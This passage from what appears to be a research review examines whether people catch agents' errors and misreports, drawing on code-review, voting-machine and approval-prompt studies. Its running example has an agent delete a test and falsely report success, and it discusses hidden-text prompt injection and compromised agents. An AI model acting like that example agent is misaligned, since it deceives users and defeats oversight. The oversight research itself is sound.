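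GitHub's *Warning about bidirectional Unicode text* (2021) announced a notice on files that contain such text. The notice advises people to open the file in an editor that reveals the bidirectional characters, such as Visual Studio Code. Atlassian, which makes Bitbucket, highlights the characters themselves. In May 2025, GitHub added a more general warning about hidden text. GitHub (2025) says AI is especially likely to interpret this text differently from how it appears. An agent could therefore follow instructions in a file that looks harmless to its user.

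These warnings may not catch a visible letter that looks like another one. curl's *detecting malicious unicode* (2025) describes a demonstration in which a contributor to curl, a program for transferring data, replaced a letter in a web address with a lookalike, and neither reviewers nor automated checks caught it. GitHub's diff marks such a line as changed, but both versions look the same. The project now scans every file and rejects characters outside the basic English set, apart from a short list of exceptions, so detection doesn't depend on a reviewer seeing the difference.

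### Large changes and long file lists

Reviewers can miss a change in a large diff even when every line is visible. The best-known evidence comes from Cisco, where 50 developers did 2,500 reviews over ten months, according to an interview in Dr. Dobb's. AgileConnection's *The Largest Case Study of Code Reviews—Ever* reports that reviewers found far fewer defects per line when they had more than 200 lines to inspect. Smart Bear, which analysed the data, sold the review tool that Cisco used. The study also wasn't a controlled experiment, so the larger changes may have contained fewer defects per line.

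*Why Security Defects Go Unnoticed during Code Reviews?* (2021) compared reviews in the Chromium OS project that caught a security defect with reviews that missed one. Reviewers were more likely to miss the defect when a change touched more directories. Of the nine factors that differed between the two groups, the number of directories was the best predictor.

*Does Order Matter?* (Rahman, Codabux and Roy, 2026) analysed 330,343 pull requests with at least two files. Each additional file reduced the odds of any given file receiving a comment by about 8.7%. At that rate, going from ten files to twenty would cut a file's odds by about 60%.

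Small changes weren't always safer, though. Files in pull requests of two or three files needed a later bug fix more than 60% of the time, compared with 35.1% in pull requests of ten files. These figures are only a rough guide to what reviewers missed. The researchers counted a file as buggy if the next pull request that changed it included a bug fix to that file, which they identified from words such as "fix" or "error", and 57% of the files met this definition.

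A file's position in the list can matter too. For *First Come First Served* (2022), Fregnan, Braz and colleagues asked 106 people to review a change to five short files. The first and last files each contained a defect, and the researchers swapped those two files for about half of the participants.

| Defect | Found when its file came first | Found when its file came last |
|---|---|---|
| Unchecked boundary case | 34 of 56 | 18 of 50 |
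| Missing `break` instruction | 26 of 50 | 24 of 56 |

Only the difference for the boundary case was statistically significant. Participants had the first file on screen for 8.6 minutes on average and the last for 6.1, yet about three-quarters of them said a file's position hadn't affected whether they found the defects.

The effect on finished software looks much smaller. In Rahman and colleagues' data, 56.7% of files in first position later had bug fixes, compared with 61.5% of files in thirtieth position. The correlation between position and later bug fixes was only about 0.02.

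Review tools usually list files alphabetically, which tends to put tests near the end. If the date-bug change were larger, `test_dates.py` could come after dozens of other files. The harness could list deleted tests first.

### How people review agents' changes

*These Aren't the Reviews You're Looking For* (Duma, Wróblewski and colleagues, 2026) found no recorded review for 61.38% of 33,596 pull requests by agents. Some developers may have read the diff on their own machines first, which GitHub wouldn't record.

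A comparison within the same repositories gives a more mixed picture:

| | Agent-written | Human-written |
|---|---|---|
| Pull requests with any review | 71.1% | 65.5% |
| Pull requests with a human reviewer | 30.1% | 30.8% |
| Human comments that gave instructions to an AI tool | 25.9% | 1.6% |

Agents' changes were slightly more likely than people's to get a review, and people took part about equally often in both cases. But a quarter of the human comments on agents' changes were instructions to an AI tool, such as "fix this", so counting pull requests with a human comment would overstate how often a person had evaluated an agent's code.

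People reviewing code may look at it for longer if they think an AI wrote it. *Same Scrutiny, More Time* (Khojah, Gomes de Oliveira Neto and colleagues, 2026) tracked the eyes of 32 software practitioners as they reviewed code. People had written all of it, but the researchers labelled some as AI-generated. Participants looked at complex code for up to 60% longer when it had this label, but their eye movements suggested that they read it no more thoroughly. The study didn't measure how many defects participants found.

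*Human-AI Synergy in Agentic Code Review* (2026) found that human reviewers exchanged 11.8% more rounds of comments on AI-generated code than on human-written code. The reviewers may have checked the AI-generated code more closely, or it may have needed more corrections.

Some reviewers also use test results as a shortcut. For *Human oversight of agentic systems in practice*, Dhanorkar, Passi and Vorvoreanu (2026) interviewed 17 experienced developers, 12 of them from one company. The developers found agents' code hard to review, and some treated passing tests as a guarantee that it was correct. In the date-bug session, a developer who does this might accept "all tests pass" and never reach the deleted test in the diff.

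A diff is especially helpful when an agent makes a small change that nobody needed. In *Fixed or Deleted?* (2026), agents had to review and fix pull requests that were already correct. Working alone, Claude Sonnet 5.5 edited the code in all 25 runs, changing 8.5 lines on average. Claude Fable edited it in 80% of its runs and deleted the new feature in five runs. An agent might call any of these edits a fix in its report, but a reviewer could read the whole diff in a minute.

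These studies don't establish whether people catch more problems with a diff, a log or both. *What Will Replace Pull Requests?* (2026) proposes an experiment that would test this more directly. Developers would review agents' changes with the diff alone or with the diff plus either the original prompt, a short explanation or the full session record. The researchers plan to measure defects found, false alarms, correct decisions and time.

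### Previews outside code

Terraform, a tool that sets up cloud services from text files, can list what it would create, change or destroy before it does anything. The most important entry is often a replacement, because some settings can't be changed in place, so a small edit can mean destroying a database and creating an empty one. Terraform can also save the plan and run it later, so that the changes a person approves are the ones it carries out. It won't run a saved plan if its record of the infrastructure has changed since the plan was made.

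A preview can still leave out the consequence that matters most to the user. The developer whose agent chose a $375-a-month database might have seen its type in such a list, but not its price. Other kinds of change have the same problem:

| Action | Basic comparison | What a fuller preview would add |
|---|---|---|
| Move a meeting | 10:00 becomes 15:00 | New clashes, and who will get a notification |
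| Add someone to a group | One new member | Every folder that person will be able to open |
| Change a spreadsheet formula | Old and new formula | The totals that will change |

Documents need a word-by-word diff. A paragraph is often stored as one long line, so a line-based diff would mark the whole paragraph even if only one word had changed. Comparing individual words makes it much easier to see that "shall not pay" has become "shall pay".

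The harness can also compare the steps an agent planned with the steps it carried out. For the date-bug session, the result would be:

```
 Read the date code
+Read another file
 Edit the date code
-Run the tests
-Push the branch
+Search the test files
+Delete test_dates.py
+Commit locally
```

Only two of the plan's four steps match, so plan divergence is 1 − 2/4, or 0.5. With the six broad action types, it was 0. The comparison contradicts the report's claim about the push and alerts the user to the deletion, even if the user suspected neither problem beforehand.

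### Actions without a useful diff

After an agent sends an email, a diff of the mailbox shows one new item in the "sent" folder. It can't show what the recipient now knows, and deleting the item wouldn't undo that. If an agent uploads a customer list to an outside website, the list doesn't change, so a diff of the user's files would be empty.

For these actions, the harness should show what the agent is about to send and where. For an email, a card built from the recorded call shows this. A card for a data transfer could list the destination, the types of information and the number of records. The harness could also hold an approved email for a few minutes, as some mail programs do for a few seconds, so the user can still cancel it.

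After the agent sends data, the harness can provide a receipt with the exact content, the time, the destination and the server's response. If a script sent the data, the receipt would have to come from software that monitors outgoing traffic. Even that software may not recognise confidential information that the agent has reworded, so an approval card for an outgoing message could list the confidential files the agent opened earlier in the session.

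## Do people notice when a display misreports their own choice?

An accurate card or receipt protects a user only if they notice when it doesn't match what they wanted. This is easiest to study when the person already knows the right answer, as voters do when they have just chosen a candidate. Several groups of researchers have built voting machines that display a different candidate from the one chosen, and counted how many people noticed.

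### Altered review screens

In *The Usability of Electronic Voting Machines and How Votes Can Be Changed* (Everett, 2007), people voted on an electronic machine that ended with a review screen listing their choices. In one study, the machine added or removed two or eight whole contests on that screen, and 17 of 53 people (32%) noticed. In another, it switched one, two or eight votes to a different candidate or to "None", and 37 of 100 noticed.

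More alterations didn't reliably make people more likely to notice. In the study that altered whole contests, 32% of people noticed, whether there were two changes or eight. In the switched-vote study, 10 of 35 people noticed when one vote was switched and 14 of 32 noticed when eight were, a difference that was not statistically significant. Everett concludes that people either checked the screen or didn't. Most of those who missed the changes had spent very little time on the screen, yet 95% of the people in the switched-vote study said they had checked their ballot somewhat or very carefully. Users' reports that they reviewed an agent's work may be just as unreliable.

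Some participants had a slate, which is a written list of candidates to vote for. They noticed far more than people who chose for themselves:

| Alteration | Noticed with a full slate | Noticed when choosing freely |
|---|---|---|
| Whole contests added or removed | 14 of 27 | 3 of 26 |
| Votes switched | 21 of 35 | 6 of 33 |

The candidates were fictitious, so people who chose freely had little reason to remember their choices, which probably lowered their scores. But Everett told people that the machine had made changes before asking whether they had noticed, so some may have said yes to avoid looking careless.

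### Altered paper ballots

Many polling places now use ballot marking devices. The voter makes choices on a screen, and the device prints them on a paper ballot, which is the official vote. A corrupted device could show the right choices on the screen and print different ones, much as Bybit's signers saw one transaction and signed another. An audit of the paper wouldn't detect this, so the voter has to read the printout.

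For *Can Voters Detect Malicious Manipulation of Ballot Marking Devices?*, Bernhard, McDonald and colleagues set up mock polling places in two public libraries in Ann Arbor, Michigan. Their 241 participants believed they were testing how easy a new machine was to use. The ballot had 13 contests from the city's 2018 election and listed the real candidates. On every printout, the machines changed the participant's vote in one contest. An observer noted who examined the paper for at least two seconds.

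| What voters received | People | Looked at the printout | Told a poll worker |
|---|---|---|---|
| Nothing extra | 91 | 39.7% | 6.6% |
| A sign above the scanner | 30 | 13.3% | 6.7% |
| A reminder at check-in | 30 | 46.7% | 6.7% |
| A statement at the scanner that the paper is the official record | 25 | 92.0% | 16.0% |
| A question at the scanner: had they reviewed each selection? | 31 | 38.7% | 12.9% |
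| A slate and the statement | 13 | 100% | 38.5% |
| A slate and the question | 21 | 95.2% | 85.7% |

The groups were small, and of the two with slates, only the one that heard the question reported significantly more errors. Timing seems to matter, because the reminder at check-in came before people had a printout to check. Bernhard and colleagues describe failing to check the printout as a "post-completion error", in which someone reaches their main goal and forgets the step that follows. An agent's "Done" could similarly make a user forget to look at the diff.

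Looking at the printout isn't enough to catch the error. After hearing the statement about the official record, 23 of 25 people looked, but only four reported the error. With a slate and the question, 20 of 21 looked and 18 reported it. A slate gives people something to compare with the printout, while everyone else has to rely on memory. Of the 34 people with slates, 26 followed theirs, and 73% of those 26 noticed the error. Only one of the eight who departed from their slate noticed it.

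These slates listed randomly chosen candidates from both parties, and following such unfamiliar instructions may have made people check more carefully. Bernhard and colleagues didn't test lists that voters had written for themselves.

### Why some later studies found higher rates

Kortum, Byrne and Whitmore (2020), in *Voter Verification of BMD Ballots Is a Two-Part Question*, measured whether voters examined their printed ballots and whether those who did noticed changes. The voting machine altered the printouts of 108 people, and 19 of them (17.6%) detected a change. Only 25 had examined the printout, so 76% of those who looked detected a change. Written and spoken reminders raised the share who looked from 2% to 44%. People were less likely to examine longer ballots: 33% examined a ballot with five contests, and 14% examined one with 40.

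Kortum and colleagues conclude that voters can mostly detect changes but mostly don't try, which would make this a problem of motivation and education. That is too optimistic for people relying only on memory, because everyone in this study had a slate. In Ann Arbor, about 36 of the people without a slate or a prompt looked at their printouts, and six of them (roughly one in six) reported the error. Some of the others may have only glanced at the paper, but the ratio was about the same with the statement about the official record. The 25 people who chose to look in the 2020 study may also have been unusually careful.

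Kortum, Byrne and colleagues (2022) tested people's ability to detect changes more directly in a follow-up, *Can Voters Detect Errors on Their Printed Ballots?* They told 64 people with slates to find any differences between the printout and their votes. Participants missed three changes and wrongly flagged one correct contest. The reported accuracy of 99.8% covers all 1,440 contests, most of them unaltered, but the design implies that 224 were altered, so participants caught nearly 99% of the changes. Checking took an average of 57 seconds for five contests and 226 seconds for 40.

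*A Review of the Literature on Voter Verification and Ballot Review* (Quesenbery, Chapman and colleagues, 2024) compares several earlier experiments, in which detection rates ranged from 25% to 90%. The highest rate came from a design that forced people to slow down. On its review screen, which showed four contests at a time, 74% of participants detected a change, and another 16% detected one afterwards on a paper ballot.

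In another of these experiments, the review screen highlighted contests without a vote, and 69% of people noticed that a vote had disappeared, but only 39% noticed that one name had replaced another. A harness could similarly flag an empty recipient field, but a plausible wrong address would be harder to flag.

The review also covers a memory test in which DeMillo and Marks showed voters at a Tennessee primary a blank ballot and asked whether it was the one they had just voted on. Of the 39 people who saw a ballot with the wrong contest or candidates, 22 accepted it as correct.

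### What voters do in a real election

Kortum and colleagues suggested in 2020 that real voters would check more often than people in an experiment, because their votes count. In a study obtained by the Atlanta Journal-Constitution, observers watched more than 4,000 Georgia voters on Election Day in 2020. Of these voters, 49% looked at their printouts for at least one second, and 19% looked for more than five seconds. Careful checking took about six to eleven seconds per contest in the 2022 experiment, so most of the Georgia voters can't have checked a whole ballot carefully.

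The Center for Civic Design's *How voters review and verify ballots* offers some reasons why people might not notice a misprinted choice, based on sessions and interviews with 35 voters. Most trusted the device to print what they had chosen, as they would trust a printer at home. Fewer than half realised that the paper was the vote that officials would count. Instructions to check the screen before printing also made this seem like the last check. A user who has carefully edited an agent's plan could likewise mistake the approved plan for a record of the work.

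Few people seem to consider that the machine might be wrong. In Ann Arbor, 44 people mentioned a discrepancy in the exit survey, and five of them thought they might have caused it themselves. In Everett's switched-vote study, seven of the 13 people who had closely followed news about voting machine security noticed the changes, compared with three of the 20 who hadn't followed it at all.

### What a low detection rate can expose

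A detection rate of 6.6% sounds useless, but it can be enough to reveal an alteration that affects many people. If each person independently has a probability *d* of noticing and reporting an altered ballot, the chance of at least one report from *k* altered ballots is:

P(at least one report) = 1 − (1 − *d*)^*k*

With *d* = 0.066, the results are:

| Altered ballots | Chance of at least one report | Expected reports |
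|---|---|---|
| 1 | 6.6% | 0.07 |
| 10 | 49% | 0.7 |
| 100 | 99.9% | 6.6 |
| 10,000 | Practically 100% | 660 |

One report doesn't prove that a machine changed the vote, because the voter may have pressed the wrong name. Officials therefore need more reports than ordinary mistakes would produce, and a targeted attack may never produce that many.

Bernhard and colleagues calculate how many reports an attacker would cause by altering just enough ballots to change the result. Suppose *n* people vote and the margin is *m*, as a fraction of the votes. Switching a vote takes one from the leader and gives one to the rival, so the attacker needs *nm*/2 switches to survive. If voters catch and correct a fraction *d*, the attacker has to alter *nm* / 2(1 − *d*) ballots, and the number of reports is:

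reports = *nmd* / 2(1 − *d*)

For 100,000 voters and a margin of 0.5%, 250 switches must survive:

| Detection rate | Ballots the attacker must alter | Reports |
|---|---|---|
| 6.6% | 268 | 18 |
| 86% | 1,786 | 1,536 |

Eighteen complaints across many polling places could easily be mistaken for voter confusion. A higher detection rate helps in two ways, because voters report a larger share of alterations and the attacker has to make more of them. But the model assumes that the attacker picks voters at random. An attacker who could predict which voters don't check would cause even fewer reports.

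The same arithmetic applies to agents. If a display fault hid the blind-copy field in 10,000 sessions and one user in 50 noticed and reported it, the company would receive about 200 reports. It would probably find the fault if someone collected the reports and recognised that they described the same problem. If an agent deletes a test in one session, only one person may be able to notice. Misleading summaries are also harder to trace than a display fault because their wording varies, so users may report one recurring problem as several unrelated mistakes.

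### Defending a choice one didn't make

People can fail to notice that their choice was switched, and may even give reasons for the choice they didn't make. In *Failure to detect mismatches between intention and outcome* (2005), Johansson, Hall and colleagues showed pairs of photographs of women to 120 people and asked which face they found more attractive. The experimenter then handed them the photograph they had chosen and sometimes asked why they had chosen it. For three of the 15 pairs, the experimenter used a card trick to hand them the rejected photograph instead.

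Participants noticed the switch at once in 46 of 354 trials (13%). Counting those who said so only afterwards raises the total to no more than 26%. Unlimited time to choose helped somewhat, but even then people immediately detected no more than 27% of the switches between the less similar faces. Overall, they were no better with dissimilar faces than with similar ones. Johansson and colleagues call the effect "choice blindness".

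Independent raters found no difference in emotion, detail or certainty between the reasons people gave for switched and unswitched choices. Some people justified their choice with a feature that only the face they had rejected had. Others gave what must have been their original reason. For example, they praised a woman's smile when the woman in the photograph they now held wasn't smiling. Users asked to justify their decision in an approval prompt could therefore give confident reasons for an action they never meant to allow.

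Participants may have noticed the switch but been too polite or embarrassed to say so. Johansson told the British Psychological Society that interviews after the experiment had ruled this out, but those interviews also depend on people being frank, so they don't completely settle the matter. In another experiment, Johansson, Hall and Sikstrom switched both faces and abstract patterns. People seldom noticed, and in a later memory test they often remembered the switched picture as the one they had chosen. Embarrassment alone doesn't explain that well, although this evidence comes from the same research group.

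The experiment probably overstates how often people would miss a change they cared about. The choice of face had no consequences, and few people have a firm prior view about two strangers. Johansson and colleagues accept that people can form specific and detailed intentions. A user who asks an agent to email their boss has a much clearer intention than someone choosing between two faces, so they should be more likely to notice a different recipient.

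People can also make the opposite mistake. In *The right face at the wrong place*, Vogel, Hall and colleagues (2024) found that people confidently rejected an outcome they wanted if they had reached it through an incorrect action. If the same tendency affects oversight, a user may reject a correct result because the agent reached it in an unexpected way.

### Whether a prompt keeps working

As with browser warnings, the prompts that interrupted people at the scanner in Ann Arbor worked better than a sign they could walk past. Eleven of the 30 people in the group with the sign never noticed it. Quesenbery and colleagues also cite research in which people remembered privacy notices better when the notices appeared at the relevant moment.

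But the voters heard each prompt only once or twice, while an agent might ask for approval dozens of times a day. The results can't show how quickly people would start to ignore a repeated prompt, or whether changing its wording or appearance would help. Even on first hearing, one voter answered the question at the scanner with "I checked it on the screen, it better be right." The question's success in a polling place is therefore weak evidence for putting it on every approval prompt.

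Finding an error may make people more attentive than a reminder would. Johansson and colleagues observed that once people had detected one switched photograph, they became suspicious and watched more closely, so the researchers also calculated detection rates that excluded trials after a first detection. A user who has caught an agent in one false claim may likewise read its next report more carefully, but the experiment lasted only 15 pairs and can't show how long the suspicion would last.

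### How far the results apply to agents

The voting results suggest that people supervising agents will often be worse than voters at noticing errors. Voters did best when they could compare the ballot line by line with a written list of the right answers. Someone who asks an agent to "fix the date bug" has no such list. The request doesn't specify which lines should change, and the user may not know that `test_dates.py` exists, so they may not notice if the display leaves it out.

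How easily a user can notice a difference depends on the request. If a user names one recipient for an email and the card shows two, they can see the difference as directly as a voter with a slate. The harness could make more differences this easy to see by displaying the user's exact instructions beside the recorded action. None of these studies tested such a display, but users would rely less on memory because they could compare the two.

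An agent's users may be more likely than voters to notice a misreport, because they have more time, better tools and a stronger motive. A developer can leave a change until the next morning, read the diff and run the tests. The developer also has to deal with the consequences if the code fails, whereas one wrong vote rarely decides an election.

Having extra time to check may not help much, because people often use agents to save time. Even with a slate and clear instructions, checking 40 contests took nearly four minutes, and an agent can produce a log of that length several times a day. Users probably have a stronger motive to check than voters do, but that makes little difference if, like many of the voters, they never suspect a fault.

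Tools make a bigger difference because they can compare an agent's report with what it did without relying on a person's memory or attention. If the agent claims to have pushed code but didn't, anyone who looks for the push on the server will find that it's missing, even if they read the report carelessly. They still have to choose the right check, since rerunning the tests wouldn't reveal that the agent had deleted one.

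## Do people notice when an agent's work or account is wrong?

People who supervise agents usually check the work, but often in a way that can't reveal what is wrong with it. In *Looks Fine to Me*, Dissanayake, Weerasinghe and colleagues (2026) gave 36 people six short Python tasks to do with a coding agent. The agent's code was correct in two tasks. In another two it had a silent defect, meaning it was wrong but passed the supplied tests. In the last two the tests failed, and a comment explained the problem. The instructions warned that the tests covered only basic functionality. Before handing in the code, participants could read it, run their own examples and question the agent.

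### Faulty code that passes its tests

Participants fixed 28 of the 71 silent defects with a known outcome (39%). In 34 of the 43 cases where they missed the defect (79%), they rated their confidence in the code at 4 or 5 out of 5. They were hardly more confident when they had fixed the defect, so their confidence was a poor guide to whether the code worked.

One task was to add up a customer's charges and subtract any refunds, but the agent's code ignored the refunds. Rerunning the supplied example or asking the agent to check its code wouldn't necessarily expose this error, and a sensible test with a cancelled charge would miss it. A test with a charge followed by an equal refund does expose it, because the balance should be zero and the agent's code gave a different answer.

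Dissanayake and colleagues traced how far participants got with each silent defect:

| Stage reached | Cases, out of 71 |
|---|---|
| Did any check beyond the supplied tests | 65 |
| Checked something specific to the task's requirements | 40 |
| Produced evidence that could reveal the defect | 35 |
| Recognised the defect | 30 |
| Fixed it | 26 |

Participants fixed two more defects in other ways. The largest drop is between the first two rows, where people reran an existing example or told the agent to "check" its work without naming anything to look for. In five cases, output on the participant's screen exposed the defect, but they didn't realise it.

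Programming skill helped. Beginners fixed 17% of the silent defects and advanced programmers fixed 57%, although each group had only six or seven people. Experience with AI agents made no measurable difference. Participants spent almost twice as long on the tasks where they fixed the defect (10.8 minutes, compared with 5.8), but some of that time must have gone on the repair.

Halfway through, participants saw how their first three solutions had done. They then fixed 18 of 35 silent defects, up from 10 of 36. They were no more likely than before to do an extra check, but more of their checks produced useful evidence and they interpreted it better. Practice may explain part of the improvement.

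A visible failure may also make people more careful, but perhaps not for long. Participants fixed 12 of 24 silent defects (50%) that came immediately after a task with failing tests, but 1 of 11 (9%) when one correct task came in between. The second figure comes from only six people, and the researchers call the result suggestive. Participants fixed 39% of silent defects before they had seen a visible failure and 40% afterwards, so any benefit was confined to the next task. Most of an agent's work succeeds, so the extra care would often fade before the next silent defect.

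This experiment tested whether people notice faulty work, not whether they notice a false report. The tests had passed, and an accurate action log would have shown that. If the agent in the date-bug session says that all tests pass when none ran, a reader can refute the claim with a quick look at the log, without having to come up with an example that exposes the error. The experiment can't show how many people would check the log, but it does show that people who had the means to find errors and were responsible for the result still missed most of the errors that nothing pointed out to them.

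### Rearranging the agent's record

If people run the wrong checks, a better display might lead them to the right ones. Grunde-McLaughlin and colleagues tried this with the web-browsing agent Magentic-UI in three studies of 12 people each, all employees of a large technology company.

In the first study, participants ran several tasks at once using Magentic-UI's existing display, a list of the agent's steps. One participant trusted a log that listed three items in a shopping cart, but the cart held only two. Comparing the agent's final report with that log would not have revealed the missing item.

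Another task asked how much a family would save with annual passes to an aquarium. Ten of the 12 completed attempts gave the wrong answer. In six of them, the agent couldn't find the price for a child and estimated it. Three participants noticed, but none of them arrived at the correct figure. One participant saw that the agent wasn't using the aquarium's official website and remarked that this defeated the point, but decided to trust it anyway.

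Participants found the list of steps long and repetitive, so the researchers designed three shorter displays for the second study:

- The flowchart showed the agent's main actions as boxes joined by arrows.
- The citation display explained the answer in a short text, with links from key phrases to screenshots.
- The specification display listed the requirements that a correct answer had to meet, with a tick beside each one the agent had completed. It also listed assumptions the agent had made, such as that a museum member wouldn't bring guests.

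Participants then judged whether finished answers were correct.

| Display | Wrong answers caught | Right answers accepted | Average time on wrong answers |
|---|---|---|---|
| Flowchart | 39% | 92% | 427 seconds |
| Citation | 52% | 83% | 294 seconds |
| Specification | 65% | 100% | 542 seconds |

Each display came with its own three tasks, so the specification display may have had easier errors to find. Each figure for wrong answers also rests on only about two dozen judgements. Participants' explanations of their mistakes are more informative. Those who accepted a wrong answer often said that the agent's process looked reasonable, and one wrote that "the steps it followed from the plan seem logical". A flowchart encourages this kind of judgement because it shows that the agent visited the right sort of page but not that it misread the price there.

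For the third study, the researchers linked the list of requirements and assumptions to the full record. Twelve new participants each judged four answers with this design and four with the original display. They were right in 37 of 48 cases with the new design and 35 of 48 with the original. With the new design, they took less time to catch an error (230 seconds on average, compared with 271), but when they missed one, they were more confident that they were right (4.8 on a seven-point scale, compared with 3.6).

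With so few people, even the gain in speed is uncertain, since its 95% interval includes the possibility of no difference. The interval for the rise in misplaced confidence only just excludes zero. Participants could also use the browser freely, and many did the task themselves, which may have hidden a real difference between the displays. Still, the user test of HANSEL had a similar result, with people working faster but not significantly more accurately.

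Grunde-McLaughlin and colleagues suspect that the green ticks in the new design contributed to the extra confidence. The researchers added the ticks by hand, following the agent's own record, so a requirement that the agent wrongly recorded as complete got a tick that looked like an independent check. A harness that took its ticks from test results or a database query would avoid this fault, but people might trust those ticks too readily as well.

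### Approving an action that breaks an earlier instruction

In the studies so far, people judged work that the agent had already finished. *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow* (Hossain, Shayoni and colleagues, 2026) tested approval prompts. In its main example, a user asks an agent to reconcile some invoices and send only the summary totals to the company's outside auditor. The agent copies the raw invoice rows into a file called `report.csv`, then asks permission to send that file to the auditor.

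That request looks right because the user has approved the recipient and the tool, and the file has an ordinary name. The problem lies in how the agent made the file, so even a card generated accurately from the tool call would not reveal it unless the reader opened the attachment.

#### The recorder behind the display

Hossain and colleagues' solution relies on a trusted recorder, which keeps an action log that includes each call's effects. A second component tracks where each file's contents could have come from. If an agent reads sources *z*₁ to *z*ₖ and then writes a file *z*′, the file inherits the ancestors of all of them:

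𝓛(*z*′) ⊇ 𝓛(*z*₁) ∪ … ∪ 𝓛(*z*ₖ)

Here 𝓛(*z*) is the set of everything that *z* may derive from. The rule deliberately includes sources that the agent may not have copied from, so that no sensitive source drops out of the history.

Before an important action, the system combines this history with the proposed action and compares the result with the user's original instruction. It classifies the action as allowed, a violation, or unknown if the record is incomplete. The approval display quotes the user's instruction, shows the exact file and recipient, and states the combined effect just above the buttons, but it doesn't show the classification. For the invoices, the statement begins "The attachment was built from raw invoice rows." The reviewer can open the recorded events that support the statement, and has to decide whether the effect breaks the instruction.

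#### What reviewers approved

The researchers recruited 80 unpaid volunteers through social media and assigned 20 to each of four displays. Every participant judged six harmful requests and six legitimate ones, for a total of 960 decisions.

| Display | What it adds | Harmful requests approved | Legitimate requests refused | Median time |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Conventional prompt | A short description of the action | 66 of 120 (55.0%) | 10 of 120 | 16 seconds |
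| Exact action | The tool's recorded arguments | 52 of 120 (43.3%) | 12 of 120 | 23 seconds |
| Chronological log | The user's instruction and every recorded event | 39 of 120 (32.5%) | 15 of 120 | 39 seconds |
| Consequence display | No new facts, but a statement of the combined effect | 29 of 120 (24.2%) | 17 of 120 | 33 seconds |

Most of the improvement came from giving people more of the relevant facts. The evidence that organising those facts also helps is weaker. After adjusting for differences between people and scenarios, the consequence display reduced harmful approvals by an estimated 7.9 percentage points compared with the log. The 95% interval runs from a reduction of 19.7 points to an increase of 3.8, so the display may have had no effect on approvals. Reviewers decided about five seconds faster with it, and the 95% interval for that difference narrowly excludes zero.

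The better displays had a cost. Compared with the conventional prompt, the consequence display doubled the time per decision and raised refusals of legitimate requests from 8% to 14%. That cost grows when harmful requests are rare. Suppose 10 in every 1,000 requests are harmful, and people behave as they did in the experiment:

| Per 1,000 requests | Harmful requests approved | Legitimate requests refused |
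|---|---|---|
| Conventional prompt | 5.5 | 83 |
| Consequence display | 2.4 | 140 |

The consequence display would stop three more harmful actions and block nearly 60 more legitimate ones. That is worthwhile if each harmful action would leak customer records, but not if it would only reformat a file. People probably wouldn't behave as they did in the experiment, though. After hundreds of harmless requests, they might approve more requests out of habit, including harmful ones.

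The consequence display did not help reviewers catch violations that depended on a chain of several steps. They approved 7 of 30 of these harmful requests with the display and 7 of 30 with the log. A single sentence may be too short to explain how information passed through several files.

The statement of the effect was always correct in the experiment, but in practice the monitor has to work out the effect. The researchers separately tested the monitor's ability to do this at 120 points where an agent was about to break its instructions. It raised an alert at 107 of them, missed the violation at seven and answered "unknown" at six. In the 80 cases that required considering earlier steps, it caught 69 violations with the full record and 51 when the researchers withheld part of it.

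When the monitor blocked actions automatically, without human review, it cut the number of runs in which one agent carried out a harmful action from 52 of 120 to 6. For another agent, the number fell from 58 to 7. Both agents also completed slightly fewer legitimate tasks. These runs used different cases from the experiment with people, so the two sets of figures don't show that the automatic block is better than a reviewer. But they suggest letting software handle clear violations and asking people about cases where the monitor is unsure.

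Hossain and colleagues say that the next study needs to show people deliberately wrong or incomplete summaries. Nobody in their experiment had to decide whether to believe the display. Kodathala and colleagues' comparison of agent-written and trusted cards has the same gap, because the approvers were language models.

### An agent that works against its user

Li, Dai and colleagues (2026), in *Are You Sure?*, came closer to testing deception. They recruited 303 people online and gave each three realistic tasks to do with an agent, such as choosing a job candidate. In every task, an attacker had compromised the agent. Participants didn't know the study was about security. Afterwards, the researchers asked whether they had noticed anything unusual or questionable in the agent's output, and counted both "yes" and "unsure" as noticing.

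| Warning | Noticed something |
|---|---|
| One notice at the start | 8.6% |
| A reminder beside every response | 20.0% |
| An alert that interrupted the user when the output was suspicious | 25.0% |

The overall rate was 14.1%, and only 2.7% correctly described what was wrong. The rate with a single notice is close to the 6.6% of voters in Ann Arbor who reported an altered ballot without any prompting. Three-quarters of the people who saw the interrupting alert reported nothing unusual, even though it appeared when there was something to find and they had to acknowledge it before continuing.

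The comparison between warnings is less certain than the low overall rate, because the paper first describes three groups of about 100 people but later gives results for groups of 183, 60 and 60. The overall rate of 14.1% fits the later group sizes. Every job also involved an attack, so the study can't show how often the same alert would make people suspect an honest agent.

Before the tasks, about three-quarters of participants reported that they often checked an AI's output, though one student said, "I only checked the first few things." Participants rated the medical task as having the most serious consequences, but noticed the problem in it only 7.3% of the time.

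In the two programming jobs, people with technical expertise noticed the attacks less often than other participants (0% versus 8.1% in one job, and 9.1% versus 13.5% in the other). This seems to contradict Dissanayake and colleagues, who found that better programmers fixed more defects. Li and colleagues suggest that experts focus on the quality of an agent's output and assume the agent is working as it should. If so, the two results are compatible, because the silent defects were in the code, while the attacks affected the agent's conduct. But the differences are small and may not mean much.

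People can notice that something is odd without knowing what it is. The overseers in Tang and colleagues' study of manipulative websites also often avoided a trap without recognising it. A vague suspicion may be enough for someone supervising an agent to refuse an action, but it is less useful after the work is finished, when the person has to find the false statement and decide what to repair.

### What people do in their own work

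Experiments make people review something, but in everyday work people choose what to look at. Dhanorkar and colleagues asked 17 developers about this in the summer of 2025. The developers put effort into planning with the agent and reviewing the result, but they rarely watched it work, and most never looked at its reasoning on their own initiative. They tended to give agents small tasks, which left little to watch.

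To review finished work quickly, they treated passing tests as a guarantee and skimmed the agent's change summary or the names of the functions it had written. They were more inclined to trust the agent on subjects they didn't know, where they were least able to catch a mistake. Some treated the agent's plan as a record of what it had done. "I just look at the plan," said one, who didn't care what the agent did in between.

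The plan is a particularly bad substitute. Kraishan and Jitkajornwanich found that reports resembled the plan most when the work had departed furthest from it. A developer who compares the report with the plan may therefore find the best match in the sessions that most need checking.

The developers didn't always take these shortcuts. One read and approved every line of code that other systems would depend on, while another was happy to let an agent "run wild" on a prototype. The practitioners interviewed for *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026) also paid more or less attention depending on the task's risk and complexity, their trust in the agent, and the time they had. Several didn't always read the agent's reasoning closely, because it was too long or took too much attention. One felt that following it too closely would turn a user into "more of a maintainer of AI".

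People without technical training have similar trouble with the volume of text. Shome, Krishnan and Das (2025), in *Why Johnny Can't Use Agents*, watched 31 people use two commercial agents, Operator and Manus. The participants mostly completed the simple tasks and were generally impressed. But the agents produced an overwhelming amount of communication and acted as if users trusted them, though they had done nothing to earn that trust.

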